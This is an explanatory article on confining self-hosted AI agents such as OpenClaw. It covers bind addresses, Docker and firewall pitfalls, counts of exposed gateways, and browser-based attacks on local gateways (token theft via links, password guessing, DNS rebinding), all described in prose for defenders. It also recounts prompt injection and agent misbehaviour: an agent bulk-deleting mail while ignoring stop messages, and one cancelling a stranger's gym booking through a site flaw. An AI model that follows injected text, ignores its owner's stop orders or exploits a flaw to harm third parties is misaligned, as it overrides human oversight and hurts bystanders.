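# Containing self-hosted AI agents: local-only gateways, certificates and limits on access to email, files and accounts

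## How a self-hosted agent works and where it can be confined

A self-hosted AI agent is a program that runs on hardware controlled by its operator, the person or organisation that runs the agent and sets its limits. The program passes requests to a language model and carries out the actions specified in the model's replies, such as running a command or sending an email. The model often runs elsewhere, on the servers of a company such as Anthropic or OpenAI. The agent is self-hosted because the controlling software and the passwords and files it works with are on the operator's hardware. People usually talk to the agent through a chat app, and it keeps running when nobody is talking to it.

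The journalist Deni Ellis Béchard described the appeal of self-hosted agents in Scientific American's *OpenClaw*. When Béchard forwarded some voice memos to a newly installed agent and asked for transcripts, the agent downloaded transcription software from the code-sharing site GitHub, installed it, ran it and saved the text to a document on the desktop. People are interested in barriers because an agent that can do this can also install something harmful if it picks the wrong program or follows the wrong person's instructions.

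### OpenClaw and similar agents

The agent in Béchard's article is OpenClaw, free software by the Austrian programmer Peter Steinberger. Researchers have studied it more than any other agent of its kind. The programmer Simon Willison (2026) traced its names through the project's revision history. The first version, dated 24 November 2025, was Warelay, a command-line tool for relaying WhatsApp messages. The project became CLAWDIS in December and Clawdbot, which many people misremember as its launch name, in early January 2026. Anthropic, whose Claude models the name played on, then asked for a change on trademark grounds. By OpenClaw's own account, the project became Moltbot on 27 January and OpenClaw on 30 January.

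The project's GitHub stars grew very fast, though stars are bookmarks and reflect interest more than installations. Willison noted 196,000 stars in mid-February. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues, 2026) reports more than 360,000 by May, the sixth highest count of any project on the site. ClawBeat's *Hermes Went From 6K to 243K Github Stars* (2026) gives a figure of about 389,000 for September, but it deserves less weight because it is an AI-generated summary of a blog post.

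Steinberger joined OpenAI in February and announced that an independent foundation would take over the project. Version 2.0, which OpenClaw's developers credited to 933 contributors, followed on 30 August. It simplified installation and added shared sessions in which several people can work with one agent. By then OpenClaw had competitors. Techzine's *Will OpenClaw regain relevance with the 2.0 release?* described its once-novel abilities as ubiquitous and the new version as an attempt to become relevant again.

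OpenClaw's nearest rival is Hermes Agent, from the AI company Nous Research. OpenAlternative's *Hermes Agent* lists much the same parts: connections to Telegram, WhatsApp and other chat apps, a lasting memory, scheduled tasks and a sandbox (a restricted environment that limits which files, commands and networks a program can use). Nvidia's NemoClaw instead puts an existing agent inside a sandbox. Most of what follows about OpenClaw therefore applies to other agents, though the default settings differ.

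### One request, from message to reply

The gateway is the system's central program. It runs continuously, receives messages, passes them to the model and carries out the model's requests. OpenClaw's *Gateway architecture* describes a single gateway that holds the connections to every channel, or messaging service through which people reach the agent. Phones and other computers can also connect to the gateway as "nodes" and give it access to their functions, including the camera, screen recording and location.

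In an example from OpenClaw's developers, your brother messages you to ask which iPad you bought for your father, and you tell the agent to find the answer and send it to him. Pirch and colleagues describe the general steps such a request follows.

The gateway first checks whether the sender may talk to the agent. It then assembles a system prompt, the text that goes to the model before the request. This prompt contains the agent's name and standing instructions, relevant notes from its long-term memory, the recent conversation, and descriptions of the available tools and skills. A tool is a program the model can call, such as one that searches a mailbox. A skill is a written description of how to achieve a goal with tools. Third parties write many skills, and a skill can include its own programs.

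The model can only return text, so it cannot open a mailbox itself. To search the owner's mail, it returns a request in an agreed format that includes the search words. The gateway runs the search, adds the result to the list of messages so far and passes the list back to the model. Once the list includes the shop's receipt, the model requests the tool that sends an iMessage to the brother. The loop continues until the model signals that it has finished or the loop reaches a maximum number of steps. The gateway then reports to the owner in the chat app. A timer or an automatic notification from another service can also start the loop, with no person involved.

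The receipt in this example is outside text, and it went into the same list as the owner's instruction. Pirch and colleagues found this mixing of trusted and untrusted text in all four agents they examined (OpenClaw, NemoClaw and two smaller ones, IronClaw and Nanobot). The standing instructions often include security advice to the model, but that advice is also just text in the list, and later text can override it. The gateway, however, is ordinary software. When it blocks a tool, no wording in an email can make the tool run unless the software has a flaw.

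### What the machine stores and what leaves it

An agent that works across many accounts keeps their credentials in one place. The following list draws on OpenClaw's *Secrets, storage, and logs*, and all the locations are in the `~/.openclaw` folder in the user's home directory.

| Location | What it can contain |
| --- | --- |
| `openclaw.json` | Tokens for the gateway, settings for model providers, lists of permitted senders |
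| `credentials/` | Logins for channels such as WhatsApp, and the senders the owner has approved |
| `state/openclaw.sqlite` | Access tokens for connected outside services |
| A database for each agent | Logins for model providers, and transcripts with private messages and tool output |
| `sandboxes/` | Copies of files that the agent read or wrote inside a sandbox |

The folder also holds installed plugins, which add code to the gateway. The transcripts are easy to overlook, but they can hold file contents, command output and secrets that someone pasted into the chat, and they may preserve an email long after the owner has deleted the original. OpenClaw masks text that it recognises as secret, but its developers still advise operators to treat the whole folder as sensitive, because any program or user with disk access can read the transcripts.

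When a provider hosts the model, the machine sends it the message list at every step. The list contains the system prompt, including any notes from memory, and the text of every email or file the agent has opened for the task. *Security of OpenClaw Agents* (Wang, Ba and colleagues, 2026) includes OpenAI, Anthropic, Google, DeepSeek and Qianwen among the providers an OpenClaw agent can use. Everything else on the disk stays on the machine until a tool reads it. The mailbox password can stay there too, because only the gateway needs it to run the search.

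An operator can stop this flow by running a model locally. But local models are often small, and the July 2026 edition of OpenClaw's *Security* warned that smaller models are more susceptible to hostile instructions. The chat service also still carries the conversation when the model is local.

### Addresses, ports and tokens

Programs on a network find each other by an address, which identifies a machine, and a port number, which identifies a program on it. A program that accepts connections does so on a chosen address, called its bind address, which determines who can reach it. If it binds to 127.0.0.1, the loopback address, only programs on the same machine can connect. If it binds to the machine's home-network address, other devices on that network can connect too, including a visitor's laptop. A gateway that answers connections from the public internet is called an exposed instance,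 even if it requires a password.

OpenClaw's gateway normally binds to 127.0.0.1 on port 18789. OpenClaw's *Security* notes that the ready-made container images, which package the software to run in a partly isolated environment, bind more widely by default and so need authentication.

A firewall permits or refuses connections according to rules, usually about address, port and direction. Inbound rules govern who can connect to the machine, and outbound rules govern what the machine can connect to. Home and office firewalls commonly block unsolicited inbound connections but allow nearly all outbound ones, so they do little to limit what an agent can connect to.

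A caller that connects to the gateway must prove it is authorised. The simplest proof is a bearer token, a secret string that gives access to anyone who presents it, including a thief who has copied it from `openclaw.json`. OpenClaw therefore also uses device pairing, in which the owner approves a device's cryptographic key once and the gateway recognises that device afterwards.

None of this closes the chat channels. A gateway on the loopback address can still receive Telegram messages, because the gateway opens the connection and Telegram sends messages back over it. A stranger who finds the agent's Telegram name can message it without connecting to port 18789, so most OpenClaw channels reply to an unknown sender with a pairing code, and the agent ignores that person until the owner approves the code.

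### How harm arises and where to set limits

An outsider can give the agent orders if the gateway's port is open and its token is missing, weak or stolen. So can a stranger on a chat channel that accepts everyone. In the experience of OpenClaw's developers, most failures are this simple: "someone messaged the bot and the bot did what they asked" (*Security trust model*). A correct password setting doesn't guarantee safety, because the software also has flaws. Pirch and colleagues counted more than 100 publicly catalogued vulnerabilities in OpenClaw by May 2026, including 5 critical and 41 high-severity ones.

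Hostile text can steer the model even when only the owner can send it messages. Prompt injection is text, placed in an email, web page or file, that a model takes as instructions. It works because the model receives the owner's request and the outsider's text together and has no reliable way to tell which to follow. Wang and colleagues give the example of an agent asked to summarise a web page that contains a hidden instruction to disclose the rest of its conversation. The attacker never connects to the agent, because the agent itself fetches the page containing the attack.

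Malicious code may run on the same machine as the gateway. It can arrive by any of the usual routes or by a new one, the market for third-party agent skills, where the security service VirusTotal documented hundreds of malicious skills in February 2026. If the code runs under the same user account as the gateway, it can read the tokens and transcripts from the disk without having to deceive the model.

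An agent can also make mistakes without an attacker involved. In February 2026 the AI researcher Summer Yue, in a post that Willison reproduced, described asking OpenClaw to suggest which emails in an inbox to delete, but to do nothing until told. This had worked on a small test inbox. The real one was so large that the software had to shorten earlier parts of the conversation to fit the model's limit, a step called compaction, and the instruction to wait was lost. The agent began deleting mail in bulk. It ignored several messages Yue sent from a phone telling it to stop, and Yue had to run to the computer to end it.

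An agent can harm people other than its owner. In August, Willison quoted an OpenClaw agent that had discovered that an Australian gym's booking site did not check who was cancelling a reservation. The agent tested this by cancelling the place of the person at the top of the waiting list, which moved its owner from fourth to third.

An operator can limit an agent's inbound connections, its outbound connections, the host machine and the accounts it uses. Each limit guards against different problems, so one can't replace another. Inbound limits keep strangers away from the gateway, but they wouldn't have helped Yue, who was the only person giving the agent orders. An account limit, such as an email login without permission to delete, would have saved the inbox because it holds however badly the model misunderstands its task. Outbound limits matter most once something has gone wrong, since an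 agent or a malicious skill that has read a private file still has to send it somewhere.

Limits on the host machine determine which files and commands an agent can reach. OpenClaw's defaults favour convenience. Sandboxing is off until the operator turns it on, and commands run without asking the owner for approval. The developers call this an intentional choice for a single trusted user. Pirch and colleagues point to a weakness that settings inside the agent do not fix. In all four agents they tested, the code that checks access to files runs with the same privileges as the code that handles incoming text, so whoever takes over that process also controls the check. Separation by the operating system or a second machine does not depend on the agent's own code in this way.

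The developers recommend deciding first who can talk to the agent, then where it can act, and relying on the model's good judgement last, because they assume someone will manipulate it. That order seems right, because Yue's instruction to wait, though clear and sensible, existed only as text in a conversation.

### One trusted operator per gateway

Designing these barriers requires some idea of whom they should keep out. OpenClaw's published approach is one trust boundary per gateway. A trust boundary is a line across which requests need checking because the other side may be hostile. In July 2026 the developers described this as a single-user model for a personal assistant. After version 2.0 introduced shared sessions, they widened it to "a single operator or a mutually trusting team" but kept one boundary per gateway. Everyone inside the boundary has to trust everyone else, and OpenClaw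 does not promise to protect them from one another.

In practice, everyone who can message an agent shares its authority to use tools. Suppose a firm connects an agent to its Slack workspace and gives it access to a confidential folder. Any employee whose messages the agent accepts can then try to get it to reveal the folder's contents, even if that employee doesn't have permission to open the folder. A document that one employee pastes in may also contain hostile text that affects the others' work.

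By default, an agent that runs outside a sandbox can list, search and read every session on its gateway, including other people's transcripts. Operators can narrow this access and assign roles that restrict what each teammate's connection may do, but the developers describe these roles as guardrails for collaboration, not as isolation between users. The project treats anyone who can edit the gateway's configuration as a trusted operator. It closes security reports without action if the attack assumes hostile users on one shared gateway.

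The developers accept a shared agent for one company team if it handles only business. They recommend giving it a dedicated machine, virtual machine or container, with its own operating-system user, browser profile and accounts, and no login to anyone's personal Apple or Google account. People who do not trust one another need separate gateways with separate credentials, preferably under different operating-system users or on different machines. Likewise, a parent who would not give a teenager the password to a mailbox should not let the teenager message an agent that can read that mailbox.

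## Accepting connections only from the local machine

A gateway that serves one operator or one team doesn't need to accept connections from most computers. A single setting, the bind address, can block those connections before any password check.

A program binds by registering a port on a particular address with the operating system. When a request arrives, the operating system matches its destination address and port to the program that registered them, without checking who sent it. If no program has registered that pair, the system rejects the request and the gateway never receives it.

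A gateway that listens only on 127.0.0.1 normally can't be reached from the network, because every computer uses that address to mean itself. A request that a laptop sends to 127.0.0.1 stays on the laptop, and operating systems normally discard packets that arrive from a network with that destination. Without a connection, an outsider can't guess the gateway's password or exploit a bug in the code that checks it. Programs already on the machine can still connect, including a web browser with a hostile page open.

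### One home computer, three settings

Suppose a desktop computer at home runs a gateway on port 18789. The router has given the computer the address 192.168.1.20, which works only on the home network. On the internet, the household shares the router's public address. The table shows who can open a connection to the gateway, whether or not they can then log in.

| Bind address | At home, behind a router that blocks incoming traffic | At home, with nothing blocking incoming traffic | On a rented cloud server |
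| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 127.0.0.1 | Programs on the computer | Programs on the computer | Programs on the server |
| The machine's network address (192.168.1.20 behind the router) | The computer and other devices on the home network | Anyone on the internet | Anyone on the internet, if the address is public or the provider maps a public one to it |
| 0.0.0.0 | The same, plus devices on any other network the computer joins | Anyone on the internet | Anyone on the internet |

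Behind the router, listening on the network address and listening on 0.0.0.0 give similar results. The router drops unsolicited requests from the internet because it has no rule for which device should get them.

The setting 0.0.0.0 is shorthand for every IPv4 address the computer has (IPv4 is the older, four-number kind), including ones it acquires later. If someone takes a laptop with this setting to a café, the gateway will accept connections from the café's network.

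A computer plugged straight into a modem usually gets its own public address, so it lacks the protection of a private network address. A cloud server normally has a public address from the start. The provider may offer a firewall, but the customer often has to configure it.

OpenClaw's setup program offers "loopback", "LAN" and a private network service called Tailscale. The Bitsight security researcher João Cruz points out in *OpenClaw🦞 (ex-Moltbot (ex-Clawdbot))* that the "LAN" option binds to 0.0.0.0, which on a cloud server means accepting connections from the internet. The option is easy to misread because LAN stands for local area network, which suggests the household.

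### How a gateway meant to be local becomes reachable

Operators often open the gateway on purpose. In Cruz's account, people wanted to use their agent from anywhere, so they rented a cheap server and chose the LAN setting. The browser then showed an error because the page was not encrypted, and the suggested fixes were to use Tailscale or open the page on the server itself. Some people instead used an option that disabled the check on the connecting device. Others installed a reverse proxy, a program that accepts connections from the internet and passes them to the gateway over the loopback address. Anyone can then reach the gateway, even though its setting still reads 127.0.0.1. Current versions reject such connections unless the operator has registered the proxy.

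A container has its own private network with its own 127.0.0.1, so if a gateway binds to that address inside the container, even the computer running the container can't reach it. For this reason, according to OpenClaw's *Network exposure*, the software binds to 0.0.0.0 when it detects that it is in a container. This doesn't put the gateway on the internet by itself, because the standard container image publishes no port on the host computer, but other containers on the same container network can connect. If the operator runs the container in host-networking mode, the container shares the computer's own network connections, and 0.0.0.0 covers all of those too.

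To use the agent, the operator normally publishes the port, which tells Docker, the container software, to pass connections from the host to the container. In Docker's usual notation, `18789:18789` publishes the port on all the host's addresses. To allow only local access, the operator can write `127.0.0.1:18789:18789`.

The host's firewall may not protect against the mistake. UFW, a common Linux firewall tool, puts most of its rules in the list for traffic addressed to the host. Docker forwards traffic for a published port to a container, so that traffic goes through a different list. An operator can tell UFW to block port 18789, see the rule in UFW's report and still have a gateway that accepts connections from the internet.

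OpenClaw's developers recommend putting the restrictions in a list called `DOCKER-USER`, which is applied before Docker's own rules. Their example accepts connections from private network addresses or to the two standard web ports, and drops other new connections. They also warn against tying a rule to a network interface by name, because the names vary between rented servers and a rule written for `eth0` has no effect where the interface is named `ens3`.

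A port-forwarding rule on a home router sends incoming connections on one port to a chosen device, which can undo the router's protection. If that device runs a gateway bound to 192.168.1.20 or 0.0.0.0, the rule makes the gateway reachable from the internet. The rule is easy to forget because it stays on the router after the experiment that needed it ends. If the gateway has to listen on the home network, OpenClaw's developers advise restricting the port to a short list of source addresses instead of forwarding it broadly.

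IPv6, the newer address system, has enough addresses to give each device a public one, so the devices in a household no longer need to share. Whether outsiders can connect then depends on the router's firewall rules. The computer's firewall also keeps separate rules for IPv6, so an operator who writes only the IPv4 version of the Docker rules above leaves the IPv6 route open. Binding to 0.0.0.0 covers only IPv4. The IPv6 equivalent is `::`, and on many systems a program that binds to `::` also accepts IPv4 connections.

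Local discovery broadcasts help someone on the same network find a port, though they don't open one. OpenClaw can announce itself through Bonjour, the system that lets a laptop find a printer. The feature starts automatically on Macs and is off elsewhere unless the operator enables it. The normal announcement contains the gateway's role, port and connection type. A fuller mode adds the port for remote login and the program's location on disk, which usually contains the user's name. An operator who doesn't need discovery can turn it off.

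In all these cases, OpenClaw will not start on anything wider than the loopback address unless the operator has configured a login.

### What OpenClaw's default was

Sources disagree on whether OpenClaw once listened on all addresses by default. The security-rating company SecurityScorecard reported that it did, according to SiliconANGLE's *Tens of thousands of OpenClaw systems exposed by misconfigurations and known exploits* (2026). But *OpenClaw in the Wild*, written about a week earlier by the internet-scanning company Censys, describes OpenClaw as listening locally by default. At that time, the project's documentation recommended using an encrypted tunnel for remote access and leaving the port closed. Cruz's walk-through of the setup program, from the same weeks, shows LAN as an option the user selects.

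SecurityScorecard's description fits an installation in a container, but the evidence suggests that an ordinary installation listens on loopback now and did so in January too. *ASTELD* (Li, Shu and colleagues, 2026) is consistent with this, attributing the exposure to Docker misconfiguration, cloud deployment or the user's own choice.

The location of the exposed gateways also suggests that people opened them to outside connections. At the end of January, Censys found at least 30% on Alibaba's cloud, though it cautioned that its view of the internet might inflate that share. By 31 March, about half were on the clouds of three Chinese companies, Tencent, Alibaba and Baidu. Often nothing blocks outside connections to a rented server, whereas a home computer with a careless setting is usually still behind a router.

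### How many gateways are exposed

The latest published count is just over 54,000 control panels, the web pages through which an owner manages a gateway. The figure comes from a Censys report with data up to July, cited in *Companies are building with AI — and exposing new security risks* (Sabin, 2026). Earlier figures ranged much higher, and two from Censys's search service differ widely despite being taken within days of each other. In late March, Etay Maor of the security company Cato Networks looked up the number during an interview and got "almost half a million", according to Claw Times. CyberDesserts ran a search on 31 March that returned 63,070, as reported in *What Censys's OpenClaw Count Reveals That February's Headlines Did Not* (2026).

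The table also draws on *The internet’s attack surface moves at very different speeds* (Pogorelec, 2026), which summarises the same Censys report as Sabin, and on a comparison of early counts by the security vendor Penligent.

| Date in 2026 | Count | What the scanner counted | Reported by |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 11 January | 2 | Control panels (Censys) | Pogorelec |
| 31 January | 21,639 | Pages with one of two titles (Censys) | Censys |
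| 27 January to 8 February | Over 30,000 | Different gateways seen at least once in daily scans of port 18789 (Bitsight) | Cruz |
| 9 February | 28,663 | Internet addresses with a control panel (SecurityScorecard) | SiliconANGLE |
| Later in February | Over 135,000 | Instances (SecurityScorecard) | Penligent |
| Late March | "Almost half a million" | Live search of Censys data | Claw Times |
| 31 March | 63,070 | Software fingerprint on four ports (Censys data) | CyberDesserts |
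| 7 April | 85,478 | Control panels (Censys) | Pogorelec |
| July | Over 54,000 | Control panels (Censys) | Sabin |

The growth in January was real. The first release with a control panel came out on 5 January, and Censys's count rose from around 1,000 to over 21,000 in less than a week at the end of the month. Much of the later variation comes from differences in method.

Censys's search on 31 January looked for pages titled "Moltbot Control" or "clawdbot Control". The project had been renamed OpenClaw the day before, so the search missed panels with the new name. This probably made little difference that day, but it would have soon afterwards. Rao's *42,900 OpenClaw Exposed Control Panels and Why You Should Care* reports that 22% of the panels in a slightly later count were already titled "OpenClaw Control".

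A scanner can instead fingerprint software, recognising it from a combination of features in its replies, such as headers and certificate patterns. This still works if the software's name changes. CyberDesserts's search used this method but covered only four ports, so it would have missed a gateway behind a reverse proxy on the ordinary web port. Nearly all its results were on port 18789.

Repeat counting can inflate the totals, since one address can host several gateways. SecurityScorecard's early data contained 40,214 instances on 28,663 addresses, according to TechRadar's *'The math is simple'*. Counting over time also inflates the totals. Bitsight's figure of 30,000 covers every gateway that appeared at any point in 13 days, including servers that people rented for an afternoon. SecurityScorecard's live dashboard rose from 135,000 to more than 220,000, according to another site cited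 by Penligent, perhaps partly because a running list that keeps old entries can only grow.

Researchers put decoy services online to study attackers. *InferD* (Hammouchi and Lenzini, 2026) describes one that imitates OpenClaw on port 18789 and is meant to be indistinguishable from the real software. A scanner could easily count a good decoy as a real gateway, and the number of decoys in the OpenClaw totals is unknown. In a similar case, Censys removed some supposed industrial control systems from its 2026 figures after a closer look suggested they weren't real.

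The half-million figure is very hard to believe. It is about eight times what the fingerprint search found the same month, and nearly twice the 267,915 addresses on which Censys found any of 44 AI-related products, including OpenClaw, in July. Li and colleagues repeat it as more than 500,000, but this adds no support, since someone read the number off a screen in an interview. *250k+ OpenClaw Instances Exposed Online*, by AI Insight Log, describes a public "watchboard" that listed 250,586 gateways, and the same comparison casts doubt on that count.

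CyberDesserts concluded that exposure fell by about 53% between February and the end of March. However, it compared SecurityScorecard's count of 135,000 with one from a different scanner, so the change of method may explain some or all of the fall. The drop from 85,478 in April to about 54,000 in July is more credible because both figures come from one Censys report. The cause is harder to establish, since some owners may have closed the port and others may have stopped using the software. As CyberDesserts points out, a gateway that disappears from a scan may still be running with all its permissions.

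### Exposed does not mean unprotected

The headline counts measure how many gateways could be reached from the internet. Most of those Censys found in January displayed a page but required a token to see or do anything more, and Sabin notes that the October figures don't establish that anyone could break in.

Authentication was sometimes weak. Cruz found that the software accepted the single letter "a" as a token. Versions released before the software was named OpenClaw could also run without a login, and people were still installing them in February. Current versions reject blank tokens and the example tokens in the documentation. Tokens under 24 characters only trigger a warning in OpenClaw's security audit.

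Bugs are the other reason to keep the port closed even with a strong token. SecurityScorecard classed 12,812 of the instances it found in February as vulnerable to remote code execution, meaning an attacker could run programs on the machine. Many were running old versions even though fixes were available. SiliconANGLE also puts the exploitable share at 63%, but 12,812 is only 45% of the 28,663 addresses, so the two figures must use different definitions or totals.

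The owner of an exposed gateway can't count on going unnoticed. Cruz quotes the operator of a decoy on port 18789 who recorded the first probes within minutes. Some visitors sent text meant to manipulate the model, while the more skilled ones bypassed the model and sent commands directly to the gateway. On 31 March, CyberDesserts found 9,993 addresses scanning that port across the internet, of which a monitoring service classed 3,282 as malicious. Other software uses the port too, so not all of them were looking for OpenClaw.

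### Tool servers and model servers

The same thing happens with other AI software. Many agents connect to outside tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in 2024. An MCP server gives the agent tools, such as one for searching a customer database. It can run on the user's machine as a local program or accept connections over a network.

In *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers*, Zhou, Zhang and colleagues (2026) counted remote servers more carefully than the sources in the table above seem to have counted OpenClaw. They collected 28,715 possible servers from two search engines and sent each one the protocol's opening message. Only 7,973 gave a valid reply. Two researchers checked a random sample of 100 by hand and found one false positive. Almost three quarters of the possible servers gave no valid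 reply, which is a good reason to distrust any count based on a search alone.

Of the 7,973 working servers, 3,233 (about 41%) required no login. Most of those the researchers sampled were tests or demonstrations with nothing sensitive on them, but one was a customer database that a company had meant for internal use. Anyone could query its more than 5,000 records, which included names, phone numbers and home or business addresses. A Censys scan in May found 12,520 MCP servers that accepted connections without credentials, according to Backlist's *Censys found 12,520 exposed MCP servers* (2026). That is far more than Zhou and colleagues found, but again the searches differed.

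The history of model servers, which run a language model for other programs to use, is even closer to OpenClaw's. The popular server Ollama binds to 127.0.0.1 by default. Hammouchi and Lenzini note that its documented configuration for several users sets the address to 0.0.0.0, so people who follow the instructions but forget the firewall end up with a public server. They cite a study of 320,102 publicly reachable model services, which found that missing logins and missing encryption were both widespread. They blame software designed for a trusted network that the operator has to provide. That seems a better explanation than carelessness, because many unrelated products have the same problem.

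This kind of exposure is still growing overall, with Censys's total for AI-related software up 63% in the nine months to July. n8n, a tool for building automated workflows, accounted for the largest share, at 113,926 addresses. It stores the passwords for every service it connects.

### Checking from outside

To confirm that a gateway is private, an operator has to inspect the machine itself and then try to connect from elsewhere. Reading the gateway's settings isn't enough, because a proxy, a published container port or a forgotten router rule may forward outside connections to it.

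Running `ss -ltn` (Linux) or `lsof -nP -iTCP -sTCP:LISTEN` (Mac) on the gateway's machine lists the addresses and ports where programs accept connections. `127.0.0.1:18789` means the gateway accepts connections only from the local machine. `0.0.0.0:18789`, `*:18789` or `[::]:18789` means it also accepts them through the machine's other network interfaces.

The outside test has to come from a different network, such as a laptop using a phone's mobile data. A test from inside the house can mislead, since many routers handle requests for their own public address differently when they come from within. OpenClaw's documentation suggests the scanning program nmap, with this command:

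`nmap -sT -p 1-65535 <public-ip> --open`

The operator replaces the part in angle brackets with the home's or server's public address. The command tries every port, since a proxy may be exposing the gateway on a port other than 18789, and lists those that accept a connection. Adding `-Pn` helps because it makes nmap scan even if the address doesn't respond to its initial probes. Without it, nmap can report that the machine seems to be down and skip the scan, which is easy to mistake for a clean result.

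The list of publicly reachable ports should be empty for a home gateway with no public services. On a cloud server, it should contain only the ports the operator meant to publish, often just the one for remote login. If the gateway's login page appears, the gateway is exposed.

If the machine has an IPv6 address, the operator should repeat the scan with the `-6` option and that address. A scan of 192.168.1.20 from another device in the house shows what a guest could reach. The operator should repeat all these checks after changing the router, container settings or hosting provider.

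A company has a harder job, because it may not know which machines to test. CyberDesserts notes that a scan of the company's registered addresses will miss an agent an employee runs on a personal cloud account, even if that agent has the employee's work passwords.

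## Why a connection from the same machine cannot be trusted automatically

A gateway on the loopback address accepts connections only from its own machine, but those connections do not necessarily come from the owner. OpenClaw's developers built early versions on the assumption that they did. The gateway put no limit on password guesses from the local machine, and it approved new devices there without asking anyone. Oasis Security acknowledged in *OpenClaw Vulnerability* (2026) that trusting local connections made sense for the intended use, because the command-line tool, the Mac companion app and the web dashboard all connect locally.

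A loopback address shows which machine a connection came from, but not who caused it. A website can make the owner's browser connect, a proxy can pass on a stranger's request, and any other program on the machine can connect on its own.

### Websites run code in the owner's browser

Most web pages include programs, usually in JavaScript, that the browser runs on the visitor's computer. If one of them connects to port 18789 on 127.0.0.1, the connection comes from the local machine, even though a stranger wrote the program.

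Browsers restrict the code on a web page through the same-origin policy. A script can normally read replies only from its page's own origin, meaning the same protocol, domain name and port. The policy doesn't cover WebSockets, the lasting two-way connections that OpenClaw's gateway uses. The browser attaches a header stating the page's origin, but the server has to check it and refuse unfamiliar sites. In January 2026, OpenClaw's gateway accepted WebSocket connections from any site, as the security company depthfirst reported in *1-Click RCE To Steal Your OpenClaw Data and Keys (CVE-2026-25253)* (2026).

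Attackers could exploit this through two separate flaws, which articles often confuse. One is known by its number in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities, CVE-2026-25253. The other is CVE-2026-32025, which Oasis Security called ClawJacked. Hackread's *ClawJacked Vulnerability in OpenClaw Lets Websites Hijack AI Agents* mislabels ClawJacked as CVE-2026-25253. The mix-up may have arisen because the US government's entry for ClawJacked, NVD's *CVE-2026-32025* (2026), appeared only on 19 March, three weeks after the announcement.

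### CVE-2026-25253: a link that gave away the token

OpenClaw's control page runs in the owner's browser and keeps the gateway's token there after login. In the affected versions, a link to the page could specify which gateway to use. depthfirst traced the code and found that the page saved the address from the link, connected to it immediately and sent the token in its opening message. Each step looked harmless alone, but together they gave the token to anyone who could get the owner to click a prepared link or visit a site that opened one.

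The stolen token alone did not let an attacker control a gateway on a laptop that accepted no outside connections. But the gateway did not check which website a connection came from, so a hostile page in the owner's browser could connect to it locally and present the token. OpenClaw's advisory, reproduced in GCVE's *GHSA-G8P2-7WF7-98MQ* (2026), confirms that the attack worked even when the gateway listened only on loopback.

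The stolen token also allowed an attacker to change settings. The attacker could use it to turn off approval prompts and make commands run outside the sandbox, without finding a bug in either protection.

Two security companies found the flaw independently, both with automated tools. Ethiack engineer Branquinho (2026) described in *One-click RCE on OpenClaw in under 2 hours* how the company's AI testing agent found it on 26 January. Ethiack reported it that evening, and the project merged the fix into its main code two days later. depthfirst published its own account on 1 February, listing versions up to 2026.1.24-1 as vulnerable. OpenClaw's advisory is the safer guide, and it lists all versions up to 2026.1.28 as vulnerable and 2026.1.29 as the first fixed version.

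Since the fix, the control page asks the owner to confirm a new gateway address before connecting. The security company SonicWall described this as a deterrent to simple one-click attacks, which seems fair because an owner who confirms without reading still sends the token. Updating doesn't cancel a token that has already leaked, so depthfirst advised anyone who suspected a leak to replace their token.

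### ClawJacked: guessing the password from a web page

On 26 February, Oasis Security announced ClawJacked, an attack on OpenClaw that didn't need a leaked token. A hostile web page opened a WebSocket to the local gateway and tried one password after another. OpenClaw limited wrong guesses, but it exempted loopback connections, which come from the same machine, and didn't log their failures.

In Oasis's lab, a script in a browser guessed hundreds of passwords per second. At that speed, a short list of common passwords can be tried in under a second and a large dictionary in minutes. After a correct guess, the script registered itself as a new device, and the gateway approved it automatically because the request was local. The researchers could then give the agent instructions from an unrelated website, with no visible sign to the owner.

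The flaw affected versions up to 2026.2.24. OpenClaw's developers fixed it in 2026.2.25, which Oasis says came within 24 hours of the report. According to their advisory, reproduced in OSV's *GHSA-jmmg-jqc7-5qf4* (2026), the gateway now checks the origin of direct browser connections even when they don't identify themselves as the control page or web chat. It also limits wrong guesses from browsers over loopback, and it no longer pairs browser clients silently unless they are the control page.

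The advisory calls the flaw "serious, but conditional", whereas Oasis wrote that any website could take over an agent. The flaw scores 7.5 out of 10 on the older version of the standard severity scale and 5.7 on the newer one. Two of the advisory's four conditions were easy to meet: the gateway had to be reachable on loopback, which was the default, and the owner had to open a hostile page. The two that mattered more were that the owner had chosen password login and that the password was guessable. A short password made the flaw very dangerous, but OpenClaw's documentation now suggests a command that generates 64 random characters, which would take longer than the age of the universe to guess at the speed Oasis measured.

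| | CVE-2026-25253 | ClawJacked (CVE-2026-32025) |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Design mistake | The control page sent its token to an address in a link | Unlimited local password guesses, followed by automatic pairing |
| What the attack required | A logged-in owner who opened a hostile link or page | An owner with a guessable password who opened a hostile page |
| Affected versions | Up to 2026.1.28 | Up to 2026.2.24 |
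| First fixed version | 2026.1.29 | 2026.2.25 |
| Main repair | Confirmation before connecting to a new gateway | Origin checks, limits on guesses and no silent pairing for other browser clients |
| Would a long random secret have prevented it? | No, because the page gave the secret away | Yes, in practice |

### Origin checks and DNS rebinding

Checking the Origin header works against websites because the browser sets it and doesn't let the page's script change it. But the check has to compare the whole name. The master's thesis *Local Network Access Standard* (van Ieperen, 2026) describes driver software from ASUS that accepted any site whose name contained `driverhub.asus.com`. An attacker could pass this check by putting that string at the start of a longer name under their own domain.

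DNS rebinding is a way around the same-origin policy. DNS translates domain names into network addresses, and the owner of a domain controls which address its name points to. An attacker first points a domain at a public server, and the victim's browser loads a page containing a script from it. The attacker then points the domain at a private address, such as 127.0.0.1, so the script's next request goes to the victim's own machine. The browser still treats this as a request to the original site because the domain name hasn't changed, and it therefore lets the script read the reply.

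In 2017 the researcher Tavis Ormandy found that websites could use this to control Transmission, a file-sharing program that runs in the background. More recently, researchers found the same weakness in MCP Inspector, which tests connections between AI models and outside tools. Both flaws let an attacker run commands on the victim's machine.

A gateway with a fixed list of permitted origins can still refuse a rebinding attack, because the origin header contains the attacker's domain. One OpenClaw setting undermines this check by letting the gateway accept an origin that matches the Host header, which holds the name the browser used to reach the gateway. In a rebinding attack, both headers contain the attacker's domain, so they match. The developers put "dangerously" in the setting's name, and an operator should leave the setting off.

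### Browsers now ask before connecting to local programs

Browser makers have added a barrier that doesn't depend on the gateway's code. Under a proposed standard called Local Network Access, a public website needs the user's permission to connect to the user's machine or other devices on the local network. The permission prompt first appeared in Chrome 142, according to the University of Illinois' *Google Chrome Local Network Access Permission*. The prompt didn't cover WebSockets at first, so Branquinho's attack worked without triggering it in Chrome 144.

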